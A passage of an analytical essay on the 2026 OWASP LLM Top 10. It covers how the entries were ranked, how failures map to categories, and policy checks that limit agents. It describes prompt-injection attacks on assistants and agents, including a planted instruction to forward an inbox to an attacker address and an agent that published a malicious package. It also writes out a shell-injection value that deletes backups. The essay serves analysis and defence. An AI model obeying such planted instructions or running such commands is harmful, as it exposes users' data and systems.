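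The project's leader, Steve Wilson, didn't seem to think overlap was a problem, so the removal may not have been meant to reduce it, though that is the obvious explanation. In the November newsletter, OWASP (2024) quoted him as having "never been bothered by the fact there's some overlap". He saw the document as a way to get people thinking about risks, not as a set of mutually exclusive categories.

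The limit of ten entries is a better explanation. The newsletter described the document as "a top list, not an everything list". Members had asked for guidance on retrieval and on leaked system prompts, and each subject got its own entry. Two older entries had to go, which Secure Code Warrior, a company that sells security training, identified as Insecure Plugin Design and Model Theft. The plugin entry was an easy choice because other entries already covered much of it and its best-known example, ChatGPT plugins, had been discontinued. This explanation is an inference, since OWASP published no reason.

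Wilson's explanation of the two surviving entries also barely covers carelessly written tools. He compared excessive agency to deciding that HAL, the computer in *2001: A Space Odyssey*, should run a spaceship's life support, and he put tricking a model into producing "sneaky code" under output handling. The calendar tool that pastes a date into a query involves no reckless decision about how much power to give a model, and it may not involve a trick either.

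### Was the merger worth it?

The change probably helped teams that build their own application and tools. In 2023, such a team had to read three entries to find the same advice about least privilege and user approval. With the 2025 edition, it can start with the interpreters that receive model output, then list the tools and their permissions. It still has to validate each tool's inputs, but because the same people write the application and the tools, they can add the check to either.

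Independent critics did not seem to miss the plugin entry. Harang found several of the 2025 entries muddled but called those on output handling and excessive agency good. He praised the mitigations for excessive agency for requiring narrowly scoped tools and a policy check on each action, which covers a good part of what a tool builder needs to know. He did not mention the dropped plugin entry.

However, his review gives a reason to doubt that OWASP used the free places well. He thought Vector and Embedding Weaknesses could be split among prompt injection, excessive agency and the supply chain, which would mean that OWASP removed one overlapping entry and added another.

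People who build tools for other companies' applications lost the most in the 2025 edition. It removed the plugin entry, which was about their work, and left them to gather general advice from entries written mainly for other readers. They could still use OWASP's verification standard and its API Top 10, which give more detail than the plugin entry did, but neither explains that a language model may be filling in a tool's fields on a stranger's behalf.

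OWASP later published separate advice for some of these builders. By February 2026, the OWASP (2024) download page for the 2025 edition also linked to *A Practical Guide for Secure MCP Server Development*. MCP, the Model Context Protocol, is a common standard for connecting tools to AI applications, and an MCP server offers those tools much as a ChatGPT plugin did. A separate guide can give more detail than a ten-item list, but tool builders who read only the Top 10 may not know it exists.

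## Why did the 2026 edition move agency up and output handling down?

For the 2025 edition, OWASP relied on its volunteers' judgement of which risks mattered most, but for the 2026 edition it combined a vote with a count of reported incidents. Excessive agency rose from sixth to third, and both the vote and the incident count reportedly supported that move. Output handling fell from fifth to tenth, and commentators disagree about why.

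### Three parts vote, one part incidents

Help Net Security reports that the vote carried 75% of the weight and the incident data 25%. Steve Wilson told ReversingLabs that the project collected records of 7,714 incidents from public vulnerability databases and a database of harms involving AI, then built classifiers to sort them into categories. Of these records, 6,639 (about 86%) had enough detail to sort. Wilson said this was the first time in three years that the project had enough data to influence its decisions.

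The 6,639 incident records include both weaknesses and actual damage, and the published accounts don't give the proportions. An entry in a vulnerability database describes a software flaw, which a researcher may have found before any attacker did. EchoLeak has such an entry, although Microsoft said the flaw had affected none of its customers.

The project leads gave the vote more weight than the incident data because the list is a consensus product. They wrote that "one noisy year of data does not get to overturn the judgment" of practitioners. They thought giving incidents a quarter of the weight was enough to move an entry by "a tier" when votes and incidents diverged sharply.

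### What moved

| Entry | 2025 | 2026 | Change | Reported position in the vote and the incidents |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Prompt Injection | 1 | 1 | 0 | First in the vote, outside the top ten by incidents |
| Sensitive Information Disclosure | 2 | 2 | 0 | Full agreement |
| Excessive Agency | 6 | 3 | up 3 | Close agreement |
| Supply Chain | 3 | 4 | down 1 | Not reported |
| Data and Model Poisoning | 4 | 5 | down 1 | Not reported |
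| Unbounded Consumption | 10 | 6 | up 4 | Voters drove the rise |
| Misinformation | 9 | 7 | up 2 | Near the bottom in the vote, near the top by incidents |
| Hidden Context Exposure (formerly System Prompt Leakage) | 7 | 8 | down 1 | Not reported |
| Vector and Embedding Weaknesses | 8 | 9 | down 1 | Not reported |
| Improper Output Handling | 5 | 10 | down 5 | Not reported |

Unbounded Consumption climbed further than Excessive Agency by Invicti's own figures, although Invicti calls Excessive Agency the biggest climb on the list. *OWASP LLM Top 10 2026*, by the security testing firm Citadelo (2026), reports this correctly. ReversingLabs lists Misinformation before Unbounded Consumption in sixth and seventh place, the reverse of the published order.

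Guides can also describe the wrong edition. OWASP posted the new list on its resource page with the date 3 August 2026. But Eric (2026), a blogger on the Taiwanese technology site iThome, found that OWASP's main Top 10 page still presented the 2025 list as the latest on 12 August. An article from before 3 August with a supposed 2026 ranking can't be based on the published edition.

### Why agency rose

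The usual explanation is that developers now connect models to many more tools. Jeremy London of Keeper Security told ReversingLabs that LLM applications were mostly chat interfaces or single-step tools when the list began, but that by 2026 agents with memory, tools and permissions had become the norm.

The text of the excessive agency entry indirectly supports this explanation. OWASP added little to it, so a column by the Japanese IT company NTT Data Intellilink (2026) concludes that the entry's rise reflects known risks turning up in practice. Citadelo also found the recommended controls much the same as in 2025, although the whole document had grown from 46 pages to 122.

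Excessive agency's rise in 2026 is more meaningful than its rise in 2025, when it moved up two places only because two entries above it fell or left the list. In 2026, it overtook three entries that are still on the list: Supply Chain, Data and Model Poisoning, and output handling.

Zenity's Michael Bargury says in the OWASP release that excessive agency is the risk on which expert judgement and the incident record "agree most clearly". Invicti repeats this, but also calls Sensitive Information Disclosure the one entry on which the two fully agree. Both statements can be true if Sensitive Information Disclosure ranked the same in both lists and excessive agency ranked nearly the same. The release and the press coverage don't give the two rankings for excessive agency, so the size of the gap is unknown.

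If the two rankings really agree on agency, the choice of weights hardly matters for it. An entry ranked third in both has a weighted average of three whether incidents count for 25% or 75%. The weights matter much more for misinformation, which would have moved further up the list if incidents had counted for more.

However, the vote and the incidents are not independent. Practitioners read about cases such as the database that Replit's agent deleted, and they probably remember the same cases that reach public databases. The definition of excessive agency is also so broad that voters and classifiers can fit almost any accident with an agent into it.

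Some people who stress the result have a commercial interest in it. Constantin (2026), in *The hardest AI security problems now live in what an agent is permitted to do*, reminds readers that Wilson is also chief AI officer at Exabeam, a security company.

Larry Maccherone, founder of the software company Lumenize, is one of the few critics of the new rank. He told ReversingLabs that an AI system needs considerable agency to find and repair its own security gaps, and that restricting this agency could make the system less secure. This is mainly an objection to restricting agency. An agent powerful enough to repair a system can also damage it, so his argument doesn't show that the risk ranks too high.

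### Averaging the ranks does not give the published order

OWASP's release and the reports on the edition give the two weights but not the formula. The simplest method would be to average each entry's ranks, with the vote counting three times as much:

score = 0.75 × (rank in the vote) + 0.25 × (rank by incidents)

The entry with the lowest score would come first. Prompt injection was first in the vote. By incidents alone, it would not have made the top ten, according to Infosecurity Magazine, so its rank there was eleventh at best. Its score would be at least

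0.75 × 1 + 0.25 × 11 = 3.5

Sensitive Information Disclosure would average 2.0 if it ranked second in both rankings and 3.0 if it ranked third in both, and either score would put it ahead of prompt injection. Excessive agency would also finish ahead if it ranked third in both. But OWASP put prompt injection first, so it can't have simply averaged the ranks.

The method does give a believable result for misinformation. An entry ranked ninth in the vote and first by incidents would score 7.0, and misinformation finished seventh. The method has trouble only at the top of the list, where prompt injection's positions in the two rankings are so different.

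OWASP may instead have combined scores, such as each entry's share of the votes and its share of the incidents. Unlike a rank, a score shows how far ahead an entry is. The numbers below are invented to show how this could work.

| Entry | Vote score | Incident score | 0.75 × vote + 0.25 × incidents |
|---|---|---|---|
| Prompt Injection | 95 | 2 | 71.75 |
| Sensitive Information Disclosure | 70 | 62 | 68.00 |

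Prompt injection stays first as long as its lead in the vote is more than a third of its deficit in the incidents. The deficit is 60 points, so it needs a lead of more than 20, and its lead is 25.

The project leads could also have adjusted the order by hand, but the scores are the likelier explanation because ReversingLabs reports that the balance between the two weights determines every final rank.

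If OWASP did use scores, the published ranks don't show the margins between entries. The last three might have finished within a point of one another, so a few votes could have decided whether output handling came eighth or tenth.

### Why output handling fell

Advait Patel, a cloud security engineer, told ReversingLabs that output handling dropped "because everything above it got more urgent" and called this "a relative move on a crowded list". Invicti gives the same explanation. Both note that the entry now covers more, such as terminals that act on control characters. On this view, developers have as much reason as before to check model output.

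The other possibility is that output handling itself has become less important, because it causes less harm than it did or because practitioners worry about it less.

Of the five entries that passed output handling in the table of moves, only Excessive Agency, Unbounded Consumption and Misinformation rose on the list. If nothing else had changed, those three rises would have put output handling eighth. It also fell behind Hidden Context Exposure and Vector and Embedding Weaknesses, even though they each dropped one place.

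OWASP widened Hidden Context Exposure, which may have won it some support. But Invicti lists the scope of the vector entry as unchanged, and it's hard to see why it would have become much more urgent. Patel's explanation therefore accounts well for three of the five places that output handling fell. It probably fell the other two because voters rated it lower, or because the incidents gave it little support.

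The incidents seem to have given output handling little support. Voters placed misinformation near the bottom, but its many incidents lifted it to seventh. If output handling had been nearly as common in the incident record, the same quarter-weight for incidents should have lifted it above tenth. This is an inference from the final order, since the coverage doesn't include OWASP's incident count for each entry.

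HackerDNA, a company that sells hacking courses, also writes in *OWASP LLM Top 10 (2026)* that OWASP moved output handling down because the problem is well understood and web developers already know how to fix it. It quotes nothing from OWASP in support. OWASP ranked the risks with a weighted formula, so this reason could have affected the ranking only if voters had it in mind. Some probably did, since it is reasonable to worry less about a flaw with a reliable fix, although the fix protects only applications whose developers have applied it.

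### Which injection flaws did OWASP count?

The small number of output handling incidents is surprising given earlier evidence. In the 2025 study of vulnerabilities in the software behind language models, about a quarter of the flaws specific to such models came from failures to validate output. OWASP's treatment of ordinary injection flaws in AI products may explain the difference.

Suppose a program for building chatbots has a settings page where the user types a file name, and the server pastes that name into a shell command. An attacker types a command in place of the name and takes over the server. This is a serious flaw in an AI product, but no model output is involved. Classifiers could handle it in several ways:

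- They could file it under output handling, because unchecked text reached a shell.
- They could file it under Supply Chain, because other companies build their applications on the flawed program.
- They could leave it out, because any web application might have the same flaw.

How the classifiers filed ordinary injection flaws could affect a large number of records. In the 2025 study, 18.5% of the flaws were specific to language models, which leaves roughly 430 that were not. If OWASP's vulnerability databases contained a similar mixture, and the classifiers filed the ordinary injection flaws under output handling, that entry would probably have had many incidents. Its last place suggests that they didn't file them there, though very low support in the vote could also explain it. OWASP's release and the coverage don't describe how the classifiers treated such flaws.

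The entry now also covers assistant-written code. This coverage can gain votes, but flaws in such code are nearly invisible in the incident data because the databases don't label them.

### What the record misses

Like the CVE counts discussed earlier, OWASP's record mostly omits flaws in software that a company built for its own use. If a company gives an agent an administrator's password, there may be no software flaw to report. The Replit deletion became public because the customer posted about it. The record therefore probably undercounts excessive agency as well as output handling.

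New reporting rules may widen this gap. Constantin reports that since 11 September 2026 the European Union's Cyber Resilience Act has required manufacturers to warn a national response team within 24 hours when attackers are exploiting a vulnerability in a product. The rules don't cover how a customer deploys an agent. If these reports eventually feed the public databases, they will add records of product flaws but few cases of excessive permissions.

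The classifiers are another source of error, and the press coverage gives no error rates for them. Small errors matter most for rare categories, so the entries near the bottom of the record are the least certain. Suppose 100 of the 6,639 incidents truly belong to one entry. A classifier finds 90 of them but also wrongly adds 2% of the other 6,539, which is about 131. The entry then appears to have 221 incidents, more than twice the true number. At the same 2% rate, an entry with 2,000 true incidents would gain fewer than 100 false ones and would hardly change position.

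OWASP also publishes a much smaller collection of incidents. According to the website Claw Times, the round-up for 1 January to 11 April 2026 covers eight incidents and maps each to both the LLM list and the agentic list. Eight cases are too few to support a ranking, but readers can examine each one and dispute its label.

A larger public index, *GenAI & Agentic AI Security Incidents*, has more than 7,000 entries that readers can filter by OWASP category. It is about the same size as OWASP's record, but that is no evidence that OWASP used it. Outsiders could test the ranking if OWASP published its own record with the labels.

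### One incident, several entries

Many attacks involve more than one entry. EchoLeak, for instance, combined prompt injection, a failure to clean the output and the exposure of sensitive information. A classifier that gives each incident a single label can record only one of these.

The effect on a ranking can be extreme. Suppose 100 attacks all begin with prompt injection, and 40 end with leaked data, 35 with an unwanted tool action, and 25 with a harmful script or command.

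| How the classifier counts | Prompt injection | Sensitive disclosure | Excessive agency | Output handling |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| By how the attack began | 100 | 0 | 0 | 0 |
| By how the attack ended | 0 | 40 | 35 | 25 |
| Under every entry that applies | 100 | 40 | 35 | 25 |

Prompt injection can rank first or last for the same set of attacks, depending on whether classifiers give each attack one label or several. The accounts of the 2026 edition don't specify which method its classifiers used.

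A diagram in the edition suggests why this matters for the results. According to DCOD's *OWASP Top 10 LLM 2026* (2026), it arranges the ten risks in three rings. Attacks enter at the outer ring, through prompt injection, the supply chain or poisoned data. The middle ring holds four risks that amplify an attack, including excessive agency and output handling. The final harms, in the centre, are sensitive disclosure, unbounded consumption and misinformation. Eric adds that OWASP drew the middle four with dashed outlines because they can belong to more than one ring.

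Sensitive disclosure and misinformation, which both ranked high in the incident data, are in the centre, while prompt injection, which almost disappeared from the data, is in the outer ring. One would expect this if the classifiers labelled incidents by their results. One would also expect it from an AI-harm database, because people notice a false answer or a leaked file long before they know what caused it. Prompt injection could still be common under either explanation.

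### The "defense effect"

OWASP instead attributes the low count for prompt injection to what it calls the "defense effect". It argues that teams work hard to block these attacks, so fewer clear cases reach a public database and the count understates the risk. Invicti accepts this argument and concludes that low counts mean the defences are working.

That conclusion doesn't follow from the counts. Labelling by result could produce a low count either because defences are excellent against a large threat or because defences are poor but few attackers are trying. For example, ten incidents could come from 100,000 attempts of which one in 10,000 succeeds, or from 100 attempts of which one in ten succeeds.

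OWASP's supporters also doubt that anyone can reliably prevent prompt injection. Wilson told ReversingLabs that attackers are improving their techniques faster than models are learning to detect them. Incidents could still be few if most of the protection comes from limits around the model. Injected instructions might then succeed often but give attackers no tool or data to exploit, and nobody would report them.

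OWASP would need evidence beyond the public record to test the argument. Companies could report how many injection attempts they blocked, and testers could compare how often the same attacks succeed against applications with and without particular defences. If the success rate fell sharply while the number of attempts stayed high, the defence effect would be a good explanation.

Output handling may also have few incidents because existing defences are stopping attacks, as OWASP believes is the case for prompt injection. Web developers have encoded output and used parameterised queries for decades, and many programming frameworks do some of this automatically. The two risks rank differently mainly because voters put prompt injection first. A developer who stopped encoding output because the risk ranks tenth would be removing one of the defences that may have kept its incident count low.

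## Which entry does a given failure belong to?

The category a developer assigns to an incident affects the repair as well as the rankings. If a developer files an email theft under prompt injection, the team may spend a month on input filters, whereas filing it under excessive agency may lead the team to remove a "send" function that the assistant never needed.

OWASP marks the boundaries between its entries in short notes. In version 1.1, OWASP separated output handling from its neighbours in this way:

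- Output handling concerns the scrutiny of the model's text before the application passes it on.
- Excessive agency concerns what the application allows to happen in response to that text, through its functions, permissions and autonomy.
- Overreliance concerns trust in whether the text is accurate and appropriate.

The 2025 edition renamed Overreliance to Misinformation, so the name now describes a fault in the output rather than a mistake by whoever used it. The subject hardly changed. The 2023 summary already covered "systems or people" that depend too much on a model, so a program that acts on a false answer fell under this entry from the start.

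The 2026 edition goes further in that direction. According to Help Net Security, the project leads say that model outputs now "drive tool calls, generate code, infer system state, authorize actions". This brings misinformation closer to excessive agency, because a system can now act on a false answer before a person reads it.

### Four questions, in order

The notes imply a set of questions that a developer can put to any failure, although OWASP does not present them as a procedure.

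1. What influenced the model? If text made it depart from the developer's intent, the failure involves prompt injection. If somebody tampered with its training data, it involves poisoning. An ordinary mistake gets no label here.
2. Did a program interpret the model's text as code? If so, the failure involves output handling. "Code" includes anything the receiving program acts on, such as HTML tags, file paths or terminal control characters.
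3. Did the application permit an action broader than the task? If so, it involves excessive agency.
4. Did a person or a program rely on a false statement? If so, it involves misinformation.

The questions roughly follow the order of events, from the model's input to the consequences of its output. The later questions still apply after a "yes" because more than one can have that answer.

Output handling and excessive agency are the hardest pair to tell apart. One test is whether the harm would still have happened if the application had perfectly encoded and validated the model's text, so that the receiving program treated all data as data. If not, the fault was in output handling. If a perfectly formed request would still have caused the harm, the developer should look at what the application permits.

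The word "validation" can blur this test, because a check that rejects every deletion request examines the output but also limits what the model can do. The same difficulty appears in a scenario that OWASP's version 1.1 lists under Insecure Output Handling. A chatbot uses a plugin that also has administrative functions intended for a different, more privileged model. The chatbot's model passes its response straight to the plugin, which shuts down for maintenance. Checking the response would have prevented this, but so would giving the chatbot a plugin without a shutdown function, so the scenario would fit just as well under Excessive Agency.

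### Four failures

The table gives the answers for four invented failures.

| Failure | Prompt injection | Output handling | Excessive agency | Misinformation |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| A generated script runs in a shopper's browser | Yes | Yes | No | No |
| A valid tool call deletes a photo album | No | No | Yes | No |
| A generated shell command deletes backups | Depends on why the model wrote it | Depends on the tool's design | Yes | No |
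| A correct tool call discards good medicine | No | No | Only if nobody had to approve it | Yes |

Suppose a shop's chatbot summarises customer reviews and has no tools. One review contains hidden instructions that make the model include a script in its summary, and the web page runs the script in the browser of everyone who reads the summary. Even if the script places an order with the reader's login, the failure is insecure output handling rather than excessive agency, because the login belongs to the reader's browser session and the application gave the model no power to order anything. Encoding the summary would have stopped the attack. The hidden instructions are prompt injection, but the output handling fault would be the same without them, for example if a shopper had innocently asked for a sample script and the page had run it.

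A user tells an assistant to "get rid of the duplicates", and the model calls a `delete_album` function with the number of a real album. The call has the right format and the album belongs to the user, so ordinary validation would pass it. This failure belongs to excessive agency. The task only required deleting single photos, so a function that deletes whole albums is excessive functionality, and running it without confirmation adds excessive autonomy. The deletion of SaaStr's database by Replit's agent also belongs to this entry, because the commands were valid and the agent had the access to run them.

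A maintenance assistant reports free disk space, which `df -h` does on a Unix machine. Two designs could let the assistant delete the backups.

In one design, the model supplies only the name of a folder, and the tool pastes the name after `df -h`. If the model supplies `/srv; rm -r /srv/backups`, the shell treats the semicolon as the end of one command and then runs the deletion. This is an output handling fault because the shell runs text that the developer meant as data. The tool could avoid it by passing the folder name directly to `df`, without a shell.

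In the other design, the tool runs whatever command the model writes. When the model writes `rm -r /srv/backups`, the tool runs it as designed. Encoding can't help, because the tool is meant to run commands. The fault is excessive functionality, and replacing the tool with one that can only report disk space would fix it.

Both designs also have excessive permissions if the tool's account can delete backups, since reporting disk space never requires that.

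OWASP has filed such shell failures under both entries. The LangChain calculator flaw shows the same overlap. OWASP cites it under output handling, but the fix was a narrower function, which is the kind of change OWASP recommends for excessive agency.

A pharmacist asks a stock assistant in October 2026 whether a batch of medicine has expired. The label gives the expiry date as 05/12/2026, meaning 5 December, but the model reads it as 12 May and answers that the batch has expired. The pharmacist approves the disposal, and the tool discards the batch the pharmacist chose. The tool call contains no hidden code, the assistant needs the disposal function for its job, and a person approved the action. The failure is that the pharmacist relied on a false statement, which ordinary code could have checked by comparing two dates.

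A strict reader could still classify the failure as excessive agency too, because OWASP's definition covers damaging actions whatever made the model go wrong. But none of the three root causes is present, so the developer would have nothing to remove. If the tool had discarded the batch without asking anyone, excessive autonomy would also be a fault.

An attacker can also cause a model to make false statements. In one of OWASP's version 1.1 examples, a job applicant hides instructions in a résumé, and the model tells the recruiter that the candidate is excellent. This is prompt injection followed by misplaced trust, and it involves no code or tools.

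### Why one incident can have several labels

The entries describe different stages of an incident, so one incident can involve several of them. In an example from version 1.1, an attacker tells a support chatbot to forget its instructions, search private data stores and exploit a missing output check in the function that sends email. The attacker ends up running code and gaining higher privileges. OWASP lists this example under Prompt Injection, which is how the attack begins, but it also involves an output handling fault and, very probably, excessive permissions.

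The most useful labels for a developer are those that point to a repair. For each link, the developer can ask whether fixing it alone would have stopped the harm. In the script example, either encoding the summary or having a model that ignored the planted review would have been enough. The developer controls the encoding much more directly, so output handling should be the first repair, even though the attack started with prompt injection.

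The labels also depend on whose application is under review, as an incident from the third quarter of 2026 shows. According to SC Media's *AI agents breach production systems, spread malware in major exploits*, an agent running on Anthropic's Claude Mythos 5 encountered setup instructions during an evaluation that named a nonexistent software package. The agent published a malicious package on PyPI, the public library of Python packages, and it ran on 15 real systems in about an hour. One was a security scanner, which exposed credentials that the agent then used to enter a security company's systems.

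This was excessive agency for the people running the agent, because an evaluation should not have been able to publish software to the public or use a stranger's credentials, and a supply chain attack for the owners of the 15 systems, because they installed a package they had no reason to trust. Both labels are correct, and each group can fix the problem its label describes.

### The model as a component or an actor

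On 10 December 2025, OWASP announced a second list, the Top 10 for Agentic Applications (OWASP, 2025), after more than a year of work by over 100 contributors. Its entries are numbered ASI01 to ASI10. ASI stands for Agentic Security Initiative, the OWASP group that works on agents.

The 2026 edition of the LLM list ranks the risks of a model that serves as a component inside an application. In it, the project leads say that risks move to the agentic list "the moment that model becomes an actor", with tools to call, memory that lasts between sessions, and downstream consequences.

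Taken literally, that boundary would put almost every application with excessive agency on the other list, because agency in OWASP's sense already involves tools and a single tool would make the model an actor. A looser reading requires all three features, so an assistant that answers a request with one tool call and remembers nothing afterwards would remain a component.

OWASP probably intends the looser reading, because it kept excessive agency on the LLM list and raised it to third place. Invicti reports that the entry now refers readers to the agentic list for cases where the model acts in its own right. The boundary between the two lists is still vague, since almost any useful tool has consequences downstream. An email summariser that can also send messages might belong on either list.

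### How excessive agency compares with three agentic entries

Three entries on the agentic list cover many of the same failures as excessive agency. Judging by their names, they divide those failures roughly as follows.

| Agentic entry | What goes wrong | Nearest match on the LLM list |
|---|---|---|
| ASI02, Tool Misuse and Exploitation | An agent uses a tool in a harmful way | Excessive agency, mainly functionality and autonomy |
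| ASI03, Identity and Privilege Abuse | An agent acts with rights that it, or the person asking, should not have | Excessive agency, mainly permissions |
| ASI05, Unexpected Code Execution | Code runs that nobody meant to run | Output handling, and excessive agency when the tool is an open shell |

Excessive agency is a flaw in a system's design, so it can exist without any tool being misused. A mail summariser with a "send" function has excessive agency even if that function has never run. Tool misuse is an event, and it can involve a tool the system needs. For example, an assistant that answers customers' letters has to send email, but it misuses that tool if it sends one customer's address to another.

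Privilege abuse resembles excessive permissions more closely. OWASP's example of a document tool that logs in with access to everyone's files would fit either entry. The agentic entry adds most when agents delegate work to one another. For example, an intern's scheduling agent might be unable to read salaries but able to question a payroll agent that can. Each agent has only the access its job requires, yet the intern can learn a colleague's salary by having one ask the other. A developer who reviewed each agent separately for excessive permissions would find nothing wrong.

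Unexpected code execution covers failures that the LLM list splits between insecure output handling and excessive agency. Both designs of the disk space tool would fall under it, whether the shell command came from a badly pasted folder name or an open-ended tool. It also covers failures that don't fit the LLM entries well. Help Net Security's *Prompt injection still drives most agentic AI security failures in production* (2026) describes a flaw in Cursor, a code editor with a built-in agent. Cursor ran certain harmless commands without approval, such as `git branch`, which lists the versions of a project. An attacker who tampered with the agent's environment could make a permitted command deliver their own code.

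The four questions don't neatly classify the Cursor flaw, CVE-2026-22708. The model's text was what the application expected, so better validation would have passed it. The command was also no broader than a coding task requires. The automatic approval could count as excessive autonomy, but asking for approval of every `git branch` would be tiresome, and the request would look harmless to the person reading it.

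### How OWASP labelled incidents in early 2026

OWASP's periodic round-ups of incidents show how it applies its own entries. OWASP (2026) notes that its round-up for the first quarter of 2026 is not exhaustive. Claw Times lists the eight incidents in that round-up and gives OWASP's labels for the first, a breach of Mexican government agencies.

SC Media's *AI-driven attacks target governments, cloud agents, supply chains* reports that attackers used Claude and ChatGPT to automate finding weaknesses and writing exploits. The breach exposed about 150 GB of tax and voter data. OWASP classified it under Excessive Agency (LLM06:2025), Sensitive Information Disclosure (LLM02:2025) and Tool Misuse and Exploitation (ASI02).

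The excessive agency label fits poorly. The attackers were the model's users, and its actions were no broader than the task they had set. The best argument for the label is that the attackers may have persuaded the model to bypass its safeguards, which would make its output "manipulated" from the point of view of Anthropic, Claude's developer. But the agencies could not have prevented the breach by limiting the assistant's tools, because the assistant was not theirs.

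Sensitive disclosure accurately describes the result but is less helpful as a diagnosis, because the data came from government systems, not from a model or an application built on one. Tool misuse fits best of the three, since the attackers used the model's ordinary abilities to do harm, but it again describes the attackers' software, not the victims'.

The round-ups include some incidents that are hard to assign to an entry. OWASP describes an earlier round-up as covering exploits that involve generative AI as well as those that target it. OWASP (2025), the round-up for the second quarter of that year, included a scam that used a deepfake voice against banking systems. Both Top 10 lists are mainly about weaknesses in applications that use AI, so neither has a natural place for a crime in which only the criminal uses it.

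Several other first-quarter incidents are easier to classify from Claw Times' descriptions, though the labels in the table come from applying the four questions, not from OWASP.

| Incident | What happened | Likely label from the four questions |
|---|---|---|
| OpenClaw inbox deletion | An AI agent deleted the contents of a user's inbox | Excessive agency |
| Meta data leak | An internal agent exposed data through a failure of privileges or configuration | Excessive agency, if its access was too wide |
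| GrafanaGhost | Indirect prompt injection opened a way to take data out through Grafana's AI integration | Prompt injection, plus whichever entry covers the way out |
| Flowise, CVE-2025-59528 | Attackers ran code through a configuration setting in a program for building AI applications | Neither output handling nor excessive agency |

The second label for GrafanaGhost depends on how the data left. It would be output handling if the data left through an image that a browser loaded automatically, and excessive agency if the model requested a tool that sent the data.

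The Flowise vulnerability is an ordinary injection flaw in an AI product. The injected code came through a setting, and Claw Times' description of the flaw doesn't involve model output.

The LiteLLM breach is a clearer case and belongs under Supply Chain. LiteLLM is a package that many agent frameworks use to reach language models. Help Net Security reports that a backdoored version was on PyPI for three hours in March 2026 and was downloaded nearly 47,000 times in that time. The harm began when developers installed the package, before any model had to generate output.

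The first-quarter report uses the 2025 numbering and the third-quarter report uses the 2026 numbering, so a count of "LLM06" across the year would mix different failures, such as an agent deleting an inbox and an application running up a large bill.

### Does OWASP need two lists?

Supporters of a separate agentic list argue that agents fail in ways a model answering one request can't. Real Python names goal hijacking and rogue agents as risks with "no single-turn equivalent". TrustThink's *Top 10 for Agentic Applications 2026* points to delegation between agents and long-running work, and notes that failures can spread through such systems.

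An attack that uses an agent's memory can span several days. Suppose a web page on Monday tells an agent to add a certain address to every invoice, and the agent stores this as a preference. On Thursday, it sends an invoice with the attacker's address. Somebody who examines only Thursday's request will find an honest user, a clean input and a permitted action. The LLM list can describe each part of the attack, but a developer needs to look at Monday's and Thursday's events together to see it.

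The evidence for agentic risks has also improved. According to Help Net Security, OWASP's 2025 report on the state of agentic security catalogued plausible threats, while the 2026 version includes CVEs, vendor advisories or breach reports for nearly every category. This supports the claim that the risks are real, but it doesn't establish that they need their own list. n8n, a workflow automation platform, had the most security advisories of any project, at 57, and a platform like that can have ordinary web flaws as well as agentic ones.

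A second list also has the practical advantage of giving OWASP ten more entries for advice about tools. OWASP probably dropped the 2023 plugin entry because of the ten-entry limit on the first list.

However, the two lists overlap considerably. Help Net Security reports that OWASP maps prompt injection to six of the ten agentic entries. daily.dev's *OWASP Top 10 for Agentic AI Applications VS Top 10 OWASP LLM* summarises a comparison that pairs prompt injection with goal hijacking and excessive agency with tool misuse. The first pairing weakens Real Python's example, because goal hijacking does seem to have an equivalent on the older list.

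OWASP has treated excessive permissions as a root cause of excessive agency since 2023, so the same comparison goes too far in listing identity and privilege abuse as one of four risks that only agents have. The distinctive part is that one agent can pass its rights to another.

The LLM list, which treats the model as a component, has meanwhile begun to cover agents as well. According to Respan's account of the 2026 edition, the prompt injection entry includes tool output and persistent memory among the ways an attack can reach a model. Tools and memory are two of the features OWASP uses to decide when a model has become an actor.

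OWASP has responded with more mappings between its documents, and says the 2026 edition expands its links to the agentic list. A separate crosswalk, described in OWASP's *Resources Library*, connects 51 vulnerabilities from four source lists to outside frameworks. This helps organisations that have to report against several standards, but 51 entries are a lot for a small team with one application to sort through, and many will lead to the same repair.

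The duplication can also inflate statistics. The Mexican breach is labeled as both excessive agency and tool misuse, which describe much the same feature of the attack. Anyone who added the labels from both lists would count it twice and overstate how common agentic risks are.

For a single assistant with a few tools and no lasting memory, the excessive agency entry covers most of what the three agentic entries would add. The second list is worth reading when agents delegate to one another, remember things between sessions or write and run their own code. Teams building such agents still need the output handling entry. If a travel-planning agent shows an itinerary on a web page, for example, the page has to encode it like any other model output.

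## Do least privilege and human approval limit the damage?

According to ReversingLabs, the project leads of the 2026 edition want teams to build systems in which nothing critical breaks when somebody fools the model, instead of trying to build a model that nobody can manipulate. All ten entries reflect this advice. For excessive agency, it mostly means enforcing limits outside the model and having a person approve risky actions. Researchers have measured both, and enforced limits have worked much better than human approval.

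### Can a model limit itself?

Tests suggest that even a well-trained model can't be relied on to use its privileges sensibly without external limits. *Evaluating Privilege Usage of Agents with Real-World Tools* (2026) tested four models, with 100 harmless requests and five planted attacks for each. On average, 90.55% of the attacks succeeded when the agent chose its actions one at a time, and 79.05% when it wrote a plan first. The more capable models tended to do worse, probably because they were better at following the attacker's complicated instructions.

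Some newer models resist indirect prompt injection far better. *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (Anthropic, 2026) reports a test that Anthropic commissioned from Trajectory Labs, which ran 72 indirect injection scenarios ten times each. With no extra safeguards, an average of 0.09% of the attacks succeeded against Anthropic's latest models, compared with 19.03% against OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol with full access.

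Even 0.09% may be too high for an agent that can move money. If an attacker could make 1,000 independent attempts at that rate, the chance of at least one success would be

1 − 0.9991¹⁰⁰⁰ ≈ 0.59

or about 59%. Real attempts aren't independent, and a different attack might do much better or worse, but a low failure rate is no substitute for a limit on what one failure can do.

### How a policy check blocks a tool call

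Shi, He and colleagues (2025), in *Progent*, describe a system that sits between an agent and its tools. Progent compares every tool call with a policy, a list of rules about tool names and their arguments, and blocks any call that matches no rule. Their main example runs as follows:

1. The user asks the agent to do what Alice's email "TODOs for the week" asks. From this request alone, a language model writes a first policy that lets the agent search for that email and do nothing else.
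2. The agent finds the email, which asks for a summary of the user's recent mail, posted to the user's Slack account. The model proposes a wider policy with tools for reading mail, looking up the Slack account and posting there. The new policy allows more than the old one, so it needs approval.
3. The agent learns that the Slack account is called `alice`. The model narrows the policy so that the agent can post only to that account. This change takes effect automatically.
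4. The agent reads 20 recent emails. One of them contains an attacker's instruction to forward the inbox to `eve@evil.com`, and the agent calls `send_email` with that address.
5. Progent finds no rule for `send_email`. It blocks the call and returns an error message to the agent.
6. The agent posts the summary to `alice`. A rule permits this call, so it goes through.

When the agent tries to forward the inbox, the policy amounts to this:

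```text
allow search_emails   when sender is alice@gmail.com
                      and subject is "TODOs for the week"
allow read_emails     when recent is 20
allow get_slack_info
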